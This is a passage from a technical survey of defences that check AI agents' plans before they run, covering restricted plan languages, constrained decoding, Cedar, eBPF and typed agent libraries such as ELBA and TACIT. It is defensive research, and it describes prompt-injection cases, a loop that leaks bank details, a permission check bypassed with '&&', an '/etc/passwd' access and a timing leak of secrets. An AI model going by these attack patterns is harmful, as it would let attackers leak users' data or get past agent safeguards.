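The loss comes more from this policy than from the restricted language. *Soteria* also uses a small plan language, whose plans consist of named states. Each move between states performs at most one action and may depend on a condition. The system complied fully with its policies on 207 tasks from three benchmarks, and its task success rate was 4.7 to 43.9 percentage points higher than the best alternative's, depending on the model and the benchmark.

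Soteria's policies regulate data flow differently from SPA's. One requires a refund amount to come from an earlier reservation lookup, whereas SPA might forbid the refund if the lookup returned untrusted data. Soteria also returns a rejected plan to the proposer and explains the error. If repeated attempts fail, it runs the best plan so far and relies on a runtime monitor to block violations. The two sets of results are not directly comparable, but they show that a restricted language can still allow high task success when the policy permits the data flows the tasks need.

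### ACE: a larger language with a weaker guarantee

*ACE* (Li, Mallick and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent that writes its plans in a restricted version of Python. The language has arithmetic, `if` statements, `for` loops over a range of whole numbers, and `while` loops whose condition is a single variable. Every variable has a declared type. A plan cannot use lists or other data that can be modified in place, define functions, or run text as code.

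Unlike SPA, ACE can add up the payments inside the loop. The central part of an invoice plan might be:

```
total: float = 0.0
for i in range(len(invoices)):
    if invoices[i].amount < 500:
        receipt: Receipt = PayInvoice(invoice=invoices[i])
        total = total + receipt.amount
```

`PayInvoice` is an "abstract app", a placeholder that ACE's proposer invents because it receives only the user's request and, optionally, a trusted description of the setting. A later stage binds each abstract app to an installed tool. It first discards tools whose descriptions are too different from the app's. A language model then examines each remaining pair of app and tool separately and writes code to convert the inputs and outputs.

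This protects the plan from malicious tool descriptions. Li and colleagues give the example of a ride-hailing app whose description tells the agent not to use a competitor. In an earlier system, the proposer read this description and left the competitor out. In ACE, the proposer doesn't see the description, and the later stage can't use one app's description to exclude another.

ACE then checks the flow of data with labels like SPA's, but because its variables can carry values from one pass of a loop to the next, one look at the loop body is not enough. Li and colleagues illustrate this with a short plan:

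```
a: str = ""
for i in range(4):
    network_send(a)
    a = load_bank_details()
```

On the first pass, the plan sends a harmless empty string. It then loads the bank details into `a`, and on the second pass it sends them over the network. A checker that examined the loop body only once, from top to bottom, would miss the leak.

ACE's checker keeps rechecking the body with the updated labels until no label changes. With $v$ variables and $h$ steps from the lowest label to the highest, labels can rise at most $v \cdot h$ times, so the process always ends. A proposer cannot write this plan in SPA, so SPA's checker needs only one pass.

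The larger language has other drawbacks. A `while` loop may never end, and the flow check doesn't test for this because it assumes that each loop runs a finite number of times. Li and colleagues also say they cannot formally guarantee that the privacy check is sound, because Python's run-time behaviour is so complex. They suggest a purpose-built language with a formal grammar as a better basis for a proof. SPA has such a grammar, but Girrens and Wang do not prove their checker sound either.

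ACE's example labels are for medical, financial and personal secrets. Under such a policy, the invoice plan would pass as long as the payment tool was cleared to see the contents of the mail, even if an email contained a false account number.

On InjecAgent, a benchmark of 1,054 prompt injection cases, ACE never called the attacker's tool. It called the tool the user's task required in 83.6% of cases with GPT-4o and 60.7% with Claude 3.7 Sonnet. But the benchmark simulates its tools and does not test whether the agent's output is correct.

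A second benchmark does measure task success, though on simple tasks. With GPT-4.1, ACE succeeded on 95% of tasks that required typing a word with a single tool, 80% when each letter had its own tool, and 85.7% of questions about a small database. One question was whether Bob and Alice live in the same city. The plan looked up both people, their locations and their cities, then compared the two city names without calling a language model.

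Girrens and Wang tried the same separation between invented and installed tools in SPA. About three-quarters of the runs failed because the system could not bind every invented tool to an installed one, and task success without flow checking fell from 53.0% to 14.1%. With GPT-4o on InjecAgent, where each task needs only one tool, ACE found a suitable match 84.3% of the time. If each match in a five-tool plan independently had the same chance of success, all five would succeed only about 43% of the time. Differences between the models and the matching methods may also have contributed to SPA's higher failure rate.

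### Can a small grammar help the proposer?

A restricted language may be easier for a model to write, partly because it permits constrained decoding. A language model produces text in small pieces called tokens, and assigns a probability to every possible next token. Constrained decoding sets the probability of any token that would break the grammar to zero, and scales up the rest so they add up to one. For example, after `"type":` in an SPA plan, the model could write only one of the six step names.

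Girrens and Wang chose JSON partly because it works with this method, and they use it for the quarantined model's answers. Constraining the plans could also help. About 19% of SPA's runs stopped before execution even without flow checking, and malformed plans are a likely cause, since SPA rejects them without a second try.

A grammar can restrict tool names to those on a list, but it can't easily require variables to be defined before use. SPA's validator has to check such rules once the plan is complete.

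Nguyen, Silva and colleagues (2026), in *Constrained Decoding*, show when the method cannot hurt. Let $Z_t$ be the total probability that the model gives to permitted tokens at position $t$ of the correct answer $Y^*$. With constrained decoding, the probability of that answer becomes

$$P_C(Y^*) = \frac{P(Y^*)}{\prod_t Z_t}.$$

No $Z_t$ exceeds one, so dividing by their product cannot lower the probability of a correct plan. Suppose a model has a 32% chance of writing the correct plan, and that at two points in that plan it would choose a forbidden token 20% of the time. The product is then $0.8 \times 0.8 = 0.64$, and the chance of a correct plan rises to $0.32 / 0.64 = 50\%$.

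The proof assumes that the grammar permits the correct answer, and that the prompt and the model's preceding reasoning stay the same. In practice, a strict format can interfere with the reasoning. *The Constraint Tax* (2026) makes this argument about models with fewer than three billion parameters. These models may need to write out intermediate results, but a schema designed for software leaves them little room to do so, and the output may be what the paper calls a "wrong answer, valid schema". A model that tried to compute a running total in SPA could have this problem. The mask would block the addition, and the model might continue with a valid plan that reported only the last payment.

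One remedy is to let the model write a draft before the constraints apply. *The Hidden Cost of Structured Generation in LLMs* (2026) tested this on school maths problems with a strict JSON format. The share of answers that were both correct and valid rose from 15.2% to 39.0% for a one-billion-parameter model, and from 49.4% to 73.9% for a 1.5-billion-parameter model. The draft helps because it makes the model more likely to choose permitted tokens even without the mask, so the mask distorts its output less.

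Nguyen and colleagues also tested eleven open models with up to 32 billion parameters. In one experiment, six of them joined the last letters of several names. When the models reasoned freely, constraining only the extraction of the final answer raised accuracy by about 3 to 6 percentage points for all six. Reasoning inside a JSON field gave clearly worse results than this for four models, similar results for one and better results for one. Nguyen and colleagues attribute such gaps to differences in prompts and formats, since constraints helped when these stayed the same.

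The choice of notation can greatly affect a model's accuracy. *Constrained Decoding for Diffusion Language Models via Efficient Inference over Finite Automata* (2026) tested Dream, a model that refines a whole text at once instead of writing it from left to right. On a benchmark of function calls, Dream's accuracy was 63.9% in JSON but only 22.4% in Python, apparently because it chose suitable functions but formatted the calls wrongly. ACE, by contrast, uses Python because current models write it well.

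The evidence for plan languages is indirect. Most of these experiments involved short answers, and Nguyen and colleagues used only simple JSON formats, whereas plans contain nested loops and conditions. It seems safest for a proposer to reason without constraints first and write only the final plan under them.

### Cedar: a language designed for analysis

Restricted languages have already succeeded in a neighbouring field. Cedar, developed at Amazon Web Services, is a language for rules about who may do what in an application. Cutler, Disselkoen and colleagues (2024), in *Cedar*, wanted it to be expressive, fast, safe and open to exact analysis, and they note that expressiveness is in tension with the other three. A Cedar rule for the invoice task might read:

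```
permit(principal, action == Action::"Pay", resource)
when {
  resource.supplier in SupplierGroup::"approved" &&
  resource.amountInCents < 50000
};
```

Cedar has no general loops, and its rules cannot change anything. It allows addition, but multiplication only by a fixed number. These limits make it possible to translate any set of rules into a logical formula that a solver can always decide. The translation is exact, so the solver gives no false alarms.

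This makes it possible to test whether two sets of rules are equivalent, which no algorithm can do for all LOOP programs. The solver searches for a request that one set allows and the other denies. If an administrator changed `<` to `<=` in the rule above, the solver would find a payment of exactly $500. In an example from Cutler and colleagues, a developer rewrites a rule that stops interns from creating task lists. The solver finds that the new version also stops them from viewing the lists they already own. In tests on example applications, such checks took 75.1 milliseconds on average.

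Cedar permits "and" and "or" in its conditions and still allows exact analysis, so SPA could probably permit them too. Girrens and Wang's ban on these operators simplifies their checker but isn't necessary for decidability.

Exact analysis does not prevent every mistake. *How We Built Cedar* (2024) explains that Cedar ignores a rule if evaluating it causes an error. A prohibition with a misspelled attribute could therefore have no effect, so Cedar includes a validator that catches most such errors in advance.

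Cedar's task is also easier than a plan language's because each decision concerns a single request. A rule therefore can't refer to earlier requests unless the application supplies that information. To stop a second payment of the same invoice, the application would have to record the first payment and pass that record to Cedar.

### eBPF: adding loops later

eBPF is a restricted language that lets users load small programs into the Linux kernel, the core of the operating system, after a verifier has checked them. Until 2019 the verifier rejected every program that contained a loop, because an endless loop in the kernel could make the machine unusable. As Corbet (2018) reported in *Bounded loops in BPF programs*, this ban excluded many useful programs. Programmers could get around it by having the compiler write out every iteration.

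A patch by Starovoitov then allowed loops by having the verifier simulate every iteration. To save work, the verifier skips a program state if it has already checked one that covers it. *Bounded loops in BPF for the 5.3 kernel* (ecree, 2019) explains that when the verifier compares states, it ignores the exact range of a value unless the rest of the program depends on it.

The verifier stops checking after processing a million instructions, so it may reject a program that would end, such as one with two nested loops of 1,000 iterations each. This is the same kind of approximation as accepting only programs that stop within 100 steps, but with a much higher limit.

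A later version of the kernel added `bpf_loop`, a function that runs a given piece of code up to about eight million times. According to eBPFChirp's *Loops and Iterators in eBPF*, the verifier has to check that code only once, because the function guarantees that the loop ends. In SPA's loop, the executor likewise controls the repetition and the checker examines the body. But programmers have to rewrite ordinary loops to use `bpf_loop`.

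*SCEV-based Loop Analysis for the BPF Verifier* (Zingerman, 2026) proposes a way to check ordinary loops without simulating each iteration. If a counter $i$ starts at 0 and rises by one until it reaches 1,000, the verifier can examine the loop body once for the whole range from 0 to 999. After the increment, $i$ lies between 1 and 1,000. The verifier has already covered these values, so it can stop on its second visit.

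The method works for values that change by a fixed amount on each pass. If a value changes less regularly, the verifier can either simulate every iteration, which is slow, or assume the value could be anything, which is fast but can cause false rejections.

Of 6,705 programs tested, 382 needed more than 10,000 steps of checking. The new method cut the work by more than half for 89 of these and by 10% to 50% for another 54. But 38 programs that previously passed now failed. Only five of them reached the instruction limit, and Zingerman was still investigating the others.

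Another proposal, the patch series *bpf*, would move the hard reasoning out of the kernel. When the verifier cannot establish a condition, it sends the condition to an ordinary program, which searches for a proof. The kernel then only has to check the proof, which is much less work.

The agent system IntentOS runs model-written plans inside an operating system kernel. According to *An Agentic OS Kernel for Flexible and Enhanced Semantics* (2026), the system's plan language keeps the values that control a loop separate from the inputs to tools and requires the plan to state them in advance. The verifier checks that the starting value, changed by the stated rule, will eventually meet the stopping condition. The result of a tool call therefore cannot keep a loop running forever. But a loop that pays invoices from an inbox of unknown size would presumably need a fixed upper limit, and any invoices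 beyond that limit would go unpaid.

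## Programs in typed languages

SPA and ACE keep plans checkable by leaving features out of the language. A designer can instead let the proposer use a full programming language, with functions, recursion and arithmetic, and rely on its types to limit what a program can do. Such a program can handle the whole invoice task, including computing the total, and a type checker still inspects it before any step runs.

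### Why agents write code

Most agents call a tool by writing a short JSON object with the tool's name and inputs, then wait for the result. In *Executable Code Actions Elicit Better LLM Agents* (Wang, Chen and colleagues, 2024), models wrote executable code instead. According to a summary in *The Bitter Lesson of Tool Calling* (Patel, Sen and colleagues, 2026), this raised success by up to 20% and took 30% fewer turns on tasks that needed several tools.

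Reducing token use soon became another argument for code. Anthropic's *Code execution with MCP* concerns agents connected to hundreds of tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for such connections. The definitions of all those tools take up space in the model's context, as does every intermediate result. Anthropic's *Introducing advanced tool use on the Claude Developer Platform* reports that the overhead can exceed 50,000 tokens before the agent reads the request. A script can search two hundred emails and return one total, so the model never has to process the emails.

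Later experiments mostly favour code. In *GeoJSON Agents* (2025), an agent that wrote code solved 97% of a set of map-data tasks, compared with 86% for one that called functions. On the hardest tasks the figures were 90% and 60%. *Fewer Tokens, Better Action* (2026) reports 14% higher success and 65% fewer tokens for robot agents that wrote code. In one episode that both kinds of agent solved, the tool-calling agent moved the robot one step at a time and looked at three camera images after each move. It used 816,000 tokens, compared with 156,000 for the code-writing agent.

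Patel and colleagues compared the two methods for 14 models on 309 items from a function-calling benchmark. Eleven models did at least as well with code as with JSON. Code's average across all 14 was slightly lower, at 77.0% against 78.6% for JSON, because three OpenAI models lost 20 to 27 percentage points. These models often wrote the characters `\n` where a script needed a line break, so the script failed to run. Code had a clear advantage when a task needed many calls at once. With JSON, Claude Sonnet 5 made every required call on items that needed up to 70, but failed every item that needed 100, while a script handled 100 calls without error. However, the benchmark's tools only returned their own inputs, so it tested whether models could write correct calls, not whether they could use the results.

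Rai (2026), in *Beyond Plain MCP*, tested complete tasks in a simulated office with 42 tools. Some tasks involved adding up invoices. Rai also tested code with and without a description of what each tool returns, such as a list of records with certain fields.

| Model | Success with JSON calls | Success with code, returns not described | Success with code, returns described |
|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3.8-27B | 85.7% | 97.5% | 99.2% |
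| Gemma-4-26B | 86.6% | 66.4% | 89.1% |
| Nemotron-3-Nano | 36.1% | 16.0% | 55.5% |

Code used 70% to 90% fewer tokens than JSON calls when the models had the descriptions, but without them two of the three models did worse with code than with JSON calls. A model that makes one call at a time receives each result before it writes the next call, whereas a model that writes a script needs the form of the result in advance. The 119 tasks came from only 21 templates and Rai wrote the descriptions by hand, so the exact figures may not hold for other tools. But the experiment suggests that declared types help the proposer as well as the checker.

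Code also gives a mistaken or hijacked model more ways to do harm. *From Tool Orchestration to Code Execution* (2026) compared the two methods on real MCP servers. Rai reports that code saved tokens and time but enlarged the attack surface, the openings an attacker can try. An ordinary Python script can open files or contact a server without calling any of the agent's tools.

### What an ordinary type check catches

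A type is a kind of value, such as a number, a piece of text or an invoice. The type checker checks that every operation receives values of the types it requires. It rejects a program that adds an amount to a supplier's name, reads a field that invoices don't have, or calls a tool without a required input.

*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao et al., 2026) lists mistakes that models made when they wrote programs in Scala 3. Several models used a plain dollar sign in a text template, where it marks a variable, so a message ending in "costs $50" did not compile. Another program looked up a customer's reservations and used an empty value, `null`, wherever a lookup failed. The compiler rejected the next step because an empty value has no status to read. The program tested for empty values first, so this was apparently a false rejection.

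These checks constrain a program's data but not its effects on the outside world. A Python function declared to take a list of invoices and return a number could also forward the list to a stranger, and its type would be the same.

### Effect types and capabilities

An effect is anything a program does besides computing a result, such as reading a file or sending money. In Haskell, types record effects. A function of type `[Invoice] -> Int` takes a list of invoices, returns a whole number and can do nothing else. Functions that interact with the outside world have results marked `IO`, and any program that performs their effects must be marked `IO` too.

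*Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) gives the example of a public calculator whose answers come from a language model. A user asks it to delete all files on the server and then compute the factorial of 5. The model writes a program that does both. The program has type `IO Int`, and the calculator accepts only programs of type `Int`, so the compiler rejects it. Haskell has a few functions that can hide an effect from the types, but a restricted mode called Safe Haskell excludes them.

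The compiler also rejects a program that deletes files only if 1 equals 2, because that program has type `IO Int` too, even though the deletion would never run. Rice's theorem implies that any sound checker for a full language must reject some safe programs in this way. The benefit of this over-approximation is that the compiler can check programs with unlimited loops and recursion without tracing how they run.

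`IO` alone is too coarse for most agents because it covers both reading mail and emptying a bank account. A library can define a narrower effect type and supply a short list of operations of that type. If an agent's program must have that type, the program can combine those operations freely but can't perform any others.

Capabilities are another way to limit effects. A capability is an unforgeable value that a program must hold to perform a given effect. In a file library by Zhou and colleagues, a value of type `Path` grants access to one directory. The function that reads files accepts only a `Path`, so a program that passes it the text "/etc/passwd" does not compile. A program can narrow its `Path` to a subdirectory and pass the result to another program, but it cannot widen a `Path`.

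Permission rules that match the text of commands are more fragile. Zhou and colleagues cite a March 2026 bug report about Anthropic's coding agent Claude Code, which compared only the first part of a compound command with its list of forbidden commands, so anything after the `&&` went unchecked.

Capabilities also let an agent write new tools safely. *L3M* (2026) describes agents that write these tools in the language Lean. A new tool can use only the capabilities that the agent already holds, so it gives the agent no new permissions.

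### The invoice task with types

A Haskell library for the invoice task might offer three operations with a custom effect type, `PayIO`:

```haskell
unpaidInvoices :: PayIO [Invoice]
findApproved   :: String -> PayIO (Maybe ApprovedSupplier)
pay            :: ApprovedSupplier -> Int -> PayIO Int
```

The symbol `::` means "has type", and `Maybe` means the lookup may find nothing. `ApprovedSupplier` is an abstract type, so code outside the library can get a value of that type only by calling `findApproved`, which checks the company's supplier table. `pay` sends money to the account recorded in that table and returns the amount in cents.

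The compiler accepts this program:

```haskell
do invoices <- unpaidInvoices
   paid <- forM invoices $ \inv -> do
     found <- findApproved (supplierName inv)
     case found of
       Just s | amount inv < 50000 -> pay s (amount inv)
       _                           -> return 0
   return (sum paid)
```

For each invoice, the program looks up the supplier and pays if the lookup succeeds and the amount is under $500. Otherwise it records zero. The last line adds up the payments, which an SPA plan could not do.

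The compiler rejects this one:

```haskell
do invoices <- unpaidInvoices
   paid <- forM invoices $ \inv ->
     pay (supplierName inv) (amount inv)
   return (sum paid)
```

`pay` requires an `ApprovedSupplier`, but the program passes the supplier's name as text, which is a type error. The type requirement therefore prevents any program from paying a supplier before looking one up.

The types also separate the two inputs of a payment. The account must come from the supplier table, but the amount may come from an email. SPA's flow rule could not make this distinction. The resulting guarantee is weaker, however. An attacker who sends a fake invoice in the name of an approved supplier can trigger a payment, although the money goes to the real supplier.

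Some wrong programs still pass the check. The types still match if the program leaves out the comparison with 50,000, pays one supplier the amount on another's invoice, or reports the sum of all the invoices instead of the sum of the payments.

A stricter library can rule out some of these mistakes. Suppose `pay` takes a value of the abstract type `Payment`, and only a function `check :: Invoice -> PayIO (Maybe Payment)` can create one. Then every payment is under the limit and matches a single invoice, as with the `check` node in the dataflow graph. A program could still use the same `Payment` twice. Zhou and colleagues suggest adding linear types, which can require a program to use a value exactly once. Even then, a program could call `check` twice on one invoice, so the library would also need to record which invoices the agent has paid.

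### ELBA

Zhou and colleagues built ELBA, a Haskell library that applies this method to agents. A developer calls its `agent` function with a prompt, a list of available functions and the required result type. The model writes a Haskell program, and the compiler checks it against that type. The program runs if it passes the check; otherwise, the model receives the error message and tries again.

The main example is an agent that compiles bibliographies. The policy requires every entry in the output file to come from DBLP, a database of computer science papers. The library has three operations, which search DBLP, fetch a record, and append a record to the file. The fetched record has the abstract type `Trusted Bib`, and the append operation accepts nothing else. All three have the effect type `BibIO`, so a program that calls Haskell's ordinary file-writing function does not compile. Between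 these calls, the model's program can use any code to sort, filter and compare records.

In a test with 100 topics, the ELBA agent wrote 925 citations, none with a false author, year or identifier. An ordinary agent with a web search tool wrote 1,002, 19 of which had such an error, and used about four times as many model calls. But the ordinary agent wrote its citations from search results and memory, so the experiment does not separate the effect of the types from the effect of copying records from a database. The types also don't ensure that a citation is relevant.

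Zhou and colleagues prove a general result about such systems. Let a trace be the sequence of tool calls with outside effects that a run makes. A property $P$ holds for a type $t$ in the host language $L$ if

$$\forall e \in L:\quad \vdash_L e : t \;\Rightarrow\; P(\text{traces}(e)),$$

which means that every program $e$ of type $t$ has only traces that satisfy $P$ as a set. The theorem is that $P$ still holds when programs of that type can also call a language model for more code. The proof replaces each such call with an ordinary function that queries the model, type-checks its answer, and either runs the answer or returns nothing. The resulting program has the same type and the same traces as the original, so $P$ applies to it. The theorem carries over whatever the host language already guarantees, but a mistake in a policy library carries over too.

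### Checks that ELBA makes at run time

ELBA's policies rely on types to different degrees:

| Policy | What the type check establishes | What the library checks during execution |
|---|---|---|
| Only DBLP records reach the file | The whole rule, if the library is correct | Nothing further |
| The agent stays inside permitted directories | Every file access uses a `Path` | Each new `Path` lies inside the permitted directory, even if it follows a link |
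| Secret or untrusted data does not reach the wrong tools | Every effect goes through the library | The labels permit each call |

For the last policy, ELBA uses LIO, an existing Haskell library that applies labels much as SPA does, but while the program runs. LIO keeps a current label for the computation and adjusts it whenever the program reads something. If a program fetches a web page and then tries to write to a trusted destination, LIO stops it with an error. The compiler accepts this program because the program's type guarantees only that LIO will check each effect.

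An agent could therefore pay two invoices, read an untrusted message and then fail on the third payment. ELBA prompts the model for a new program only after a type error, when nothing has run yet, and not after an error from LIO.

A program can avoid some of these failures by reading untrusted data in a separate computation, which returns its result wrapped in a labelled value. The main program can pass this value to a tool without reading the contents, so the program's label does not change.

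### ELBA's security tests

Zhou and colleagues compared ELBA with CaMeL on the 21 Slack tasks in AgentDojo. CaMeL is an agent that plans from the user's request alone and tracks the sources of values as its plan runs. The table shows how many tasks each system completed when there was no attack.

| Model | ELBA, with policies | CaMeL, with policies | ELBA, no policies | CaMeL, no policies |
|---|---|---|---|---|
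| Claude Opus 4.7 | 10 | 5 | 18 | 15 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 9 | 6 | 16 | 16 |
| GPT-5.4 | 10 | 5 | 16 | 17 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 8 | 4 | 14 | 13 |

With so few tasks, some of these differences could be chance. Attacked runs provide more data. ELBA with policies completed 40 to 52 of 105 attacked cases in each setting, while CaMeL completed 22 to 30. ELBA can write new code in response to what it reads, which helps it finish tasks but makes it take about three times as long. The two systems also enforced different policies, so the comparison does not show how much of ELBA's lead comes from the language.

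None of these attacks succeeded against either system, even with policies off, because the models didn't follow the attacker's instructions. To test the policies, Zhou and colleagues made the models follow them. ELBA handles incoming data in separate model calls. Whenever that data contained an attack, the researchers removed the user's task from the prompt and left only the data, so the model carried out the attacker's instructions. They ran all 105 combinations of task and attack seven times, for 735 cases per model.

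| Model | Injections resisted, with policies | Tasks completed, with policies | Injections resisted, no policies | Tasks completed, no policies |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 735 | 351 | 425 | 523 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 735 | 312 | 460 | 557 |
| GPT-5.4 | 735 | 338 | 621 | 558 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 735 | 294 | 540 | 494 |

Without policies, 16% to 42% of the injections succeeded, depending on the model, while none succeeded with policies. AgentDojo's scoring program counted 29 of the 2,940 protected runs as successful attacks because the agent had opened a certain web address, but Zhou and colleagues reviewed all 29 and found no breach of the policy. The result is largely due to LIO's runtime checks, since the type check only ensures that programs cannot bypass them.

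The policies reduced task completion from 67–76% to 40–48%. As with SPA, this is mainly because the rules about data also block legitimate steps. The model had little trouble with the language. On AgentDojo, runs needed 0.13 retries on average, and the model failed to produce a well-typed program in 7 of 2,688 runs.

SPA allows no retries, although retries cannot make a sound type checker accept an unsafe program. If the checker has a bug, however, retries give a hostile proposer more chances to find it.

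### TACIT

Odersky and colleagues take the capability approach further with TACIT, which runs agent-written programs in Scala 3. TACIT can let one part of a program use the network and another part read secrets, while forbidding any effects in the part that reads secrets. A single effect type for the whole program cannot express this rule.

A sandbox, which confines a program to certain files and servers, cannot enforce this either. An agent may have good reasons both to read a private file and to contact the company that hosts its language model. A sandbox that allows both actions also allows the agent to leak the file's contents to that company.

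Scala's compiler can record in a value's type which capabilities the value holds on to, in what is called a capture set. Suppose `archive` is a capability to write to a file. A function that takes text and writes it there has this type:

```scala
String ->{archive} Unit
```

`Unit` means the function returns nothing of interest, and the braces contain the capture set. A function of type `String -> Unit`, without braces, holds no capabilities. It is pure, meaning it can compute but has no effects.

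TACIT wraps secret data in a type called `Classified`. A program cannot take the data out, but it can use `map` to apply a function to it, and `map` accepts only pure functions. If `statement` is a classified bank statement, the compiler treats these two lines differently:

```scala
statement.map { text => text.length }          // accepted
statement.map { text => archive.write(text) }  // rejected
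```

The result of the accepted line is classified. The rejected line fails because its function captures `archive`, and `map` requires a function with an empty capture set.

Capture sets also limit how long a permission lasts. A program gets access to files inside a block of code, and no value that leaves the block may capture that access. One agent in the tests tried to return a list of open file handles from such a block, and the compiler rejected the program.

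A program could bypass these protections by using features that hide a value's type from the compiler, such as unchecked conversions between types. TACIT therefore compiles agents' programs in a safe mode that forbids such features. Safe mode allows exceptions, the errors that interrupt a program, but their messages could contain secrets, so TACIT catches them during execution. It also checks file paths, server names and commands during execution, because those checks depend on actual values.

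Classified data never reaches the agent's own model. When a program prints a classified value, the user sees the content, but the model receives only `Classified(****)`. If a task requires reading the content, the program can pass it to a separate, trusted model, whose answer is also classified.

The guarantee depends on the compiler, the library and the trusted model. Machine-checked proofs exist for the core of the type system, but Odersky and colleagues note that there is still no proof for safe mode as a whole.

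### TACIT's security and performance tests

For the security test, an agent worked on a software project with a folder of secrets, such as passwords for online services. Twelve ordinary tasks, each combined with ten injection attacks, gave 120 trials. In another 11 trials, the user asked for the secrets directly or pretended to be someone entitled to them. Each model ran all 131 trials twice, once with the secrets classified and once with them as plain text.

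| Model | Secrets | No leak in injection trials | No leak with malicious users | No leak overall | Ordinary tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | Classified | 120 of 120 | 11 of 11 | 100% | 99.2% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | Plain text | 120 of 120 | 9 of 11 | 98.5% | 83.3% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | Classified | 120 of 120 | 11 of 11 | 100% | 90.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | Plain text | 117 of 120 | 3 of 11 | 91.6% | 88.3% |

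The types made the most difference when users were malicious, a case where the models' own resistance varied widely. They did not reduce the number of tasks completed. Sonnet's low score with plain text may come from the setup, since Sonnet often ran out of time or stopped to warn the user about an injection.

Odersky and colleagues also ran TACIT on all four AgentDojo environments with two older models. Only one attack was counted as successful, and that was a scoring error, because the agent had quoted hotel reviews that mentioned the attacker's hotel. Odersky and colleagues describe task success as comparable to CaMeL's published results, but with OpenAI's o4-mini, TACIT completed only 53% of workspace tasks and 48% of Slack tasks, compared with 81% and 69% for CaMeL.

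The agent's instructions for these AgentDojo runs were to keep functions inside `map` pure "when possible", which suggests that the compiler did not treat every tool as an effect. In that case, an agent could read an account number from a classified bill and send a payment to it inside `map`. `Classified` protects the bill's secrecy but provides no evidence that the account number is genuine. For that, the payment tool would need an abstract type such as `ApprovedSupplier`.

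Odersky and colleagues compared TACIT with ordinary tool calls on two general benchmarks to find out whether typed programs make agents less capable. The benchmarks were τ²-bench, which simulates customer service for an airline and a shop, and SWE-bench Lite, which contains 300 real software bugs.

| Model | Method | Airline | Retail | SWE-bench Lite |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b | Tool calls | 43.8% | 53.3% | – |
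| gpt-oss-120b | TACIT | 45.2% | 57.0% | – |
| MiniMax M2.5 | Tool calls | 58.4% | 75.1% | 43.3% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | TACIT | 61.0% | 77.5% | 41.7% |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | Tool calls | 57.8% | 74.6% | – |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | TACIT | 58.6% | 75.5% | – |

TACIT's agents did slightly better in customer service than agents that did not write code, and solved five fewer of the 300 bugs. Writing code may have helped them while the type restrictions held them back, and this comparison can't separate the two effects. Measuring the effect of the types alone would require a comparison with agents that write untyped code.

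On τ²-bench, between 0.3% and 7.9% of the programs needed a retry, depending on the model and the domain. These usually compiled after one or two more attempts. Compilation normally took less than a second, so the type check added little delay.

The types also let the compiler check large programs quickly. In a language where functions can be passed as values, a checker without capture sets would have to work out which functions each call might reach. Odersky and colleagues point out that precise forms of this analysis are EXPTIME-complete, so their worst-case running time grows exponentially with the size of the program. With capture sets, the compiler can check each function separately, using only the declared types of the functions it calls.

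Someone has to write those declarations. TACIT's shared library is about 1,000 lines, and the declarations for the airline and retail tools are a few hundred lines each, about as long as the JSON descriptions they replaced.

### Languages designed for agents

ELBA and TACIT use existing languages, which models have been trained on. Other designers have created new languages. *ETAS* (2026) describes one in which a developer lists the effects an agent may have, such as calling a model or reading a code repository. The compiler also checks the order of the effects against a state machine, as Agentproof does for workflow graphs. In Haskell or Scala, a developer would have to enforce "approval before payment" by making the approval return a value that the payment requires.

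Pact is a typed language for agent workflows in which questions to people, tool calls and model reasoning are all typed expressions. In ELBA, the developer fixes the policy and the model writes programs that must obey it. In Pact, the model can also write new types, workflows and restrictions on later operations, and Pact checks each one against the surrounding program as soon as the model produces it. A recovery mechanism handles failures during long tasks. Pact's developers report that it cut the model's output to nearly a third and halved the running time compared with workflows that rely on assertions.

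### What types leave open

The policies in ELBA and TACIT limit what a program may do, but they don't ensure that it does its task correctly. For example, a program that pays nobody and reports a total of zero satisfies every type in the invoice library. Richer types can express more of the task, but someone then has to define a correct result formally.

Types in Haskell and Scala also do not guarantee that a program ends. The calculator program that must return an `Int` could run forever, so the executor needs a time limit. Zhou and colleagues mention type systems that limit a program's resource use or prove that it ends, but ELBA does not include them yet.

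A program that computes on secrets can leak them through timing. A pure function inside `map` could run for ten seconds if the first binary digit of an account number is 1, and finish at once if it is 0. The agent learns the digit by timing the program, and could recover a ten-digit account number with at most 34 such measurements. Odersky and colleagues state that TACIT's guarantee does not cover timing leaks or leaks through whether a program ends.

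The guarantee also does not cover code outside the language. If an agent has permission to start an external program, the compiler can check that permission but not what the program does. Odersky and colleagues recommend allowing only specific, safe commands and running TACIT inside a sandbox as well.

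## Tool contracts, proofs and steps the checker cannot see into

To reject a well-typed program that pays nobody, a checker needs a description of what each tool does and a statement of what the plan should achieve. Both can take the form of a contract with three parts. The precondition must hold before the tool or plan runs, for example that an input file exists, as in *StateMirror* (2026). The postcondition holds afterwards. The frame condition states what stays the same. A contract for the payment tool might be:

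```
pay(inv)
  requires  inv is unpaid and its supplier is approved
  ensures   inv is paid and the balance is lower by inv.amount
  frame     nothing else changes
```

The Hoare triple $\{P\}\,C\,\{Q\}$ means that if $P$ holds before $C$ runs, then $Q$ holds when $C$ finishes. Some versions also require a proof that $C$ finishes.

PDDL actions have preconditions and effects too, but PDDL assumes that an action changes only the facts it lists. In many other notations, a postcondition covers only what it mentions, so the checker must assume that anything else may have changed.

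### Deleting two files

*Guardians of the Agents* (Meijer, 2025) shows what can go wrong without frame conditions. In Meijer's design, the model writes a complete workflow, and a verifier checks it before it runs. A user asks the agent to delete foo.txt and bar.txt. The deletion tool accepts a pattern, so the model writes a single call with the pattern "*.txt", which is shorter than two calls. If the folder also contains notes.txt, the call will delete that file too.

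Let $F$ be the set of files before a call or plan runs and $F'$ the set afterwards. The postcondition of the tool is that no file matching the pattern $p$ remains:

$$\forall f:\; f \in \text{glob}(p) \Rightarrow f \notin F'.$$

The postcondition of the plan is that the two files are gone:

$$\text{foo.txt} \notin F' \;\wedge\; \text{bar.txt} \notin F'.$$

Both names match "*.txt", so the verifier accepts the plan. The plan also deletes notes.txt, which its contract doesn't mention.

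Meijer's remedy is to add a frame condition to the tool, so that files outside the pattern stay as they were. This isn't enough to reject the plan, because notes.txt is inside the pattern. The plan's own contract also needs a frame condition:

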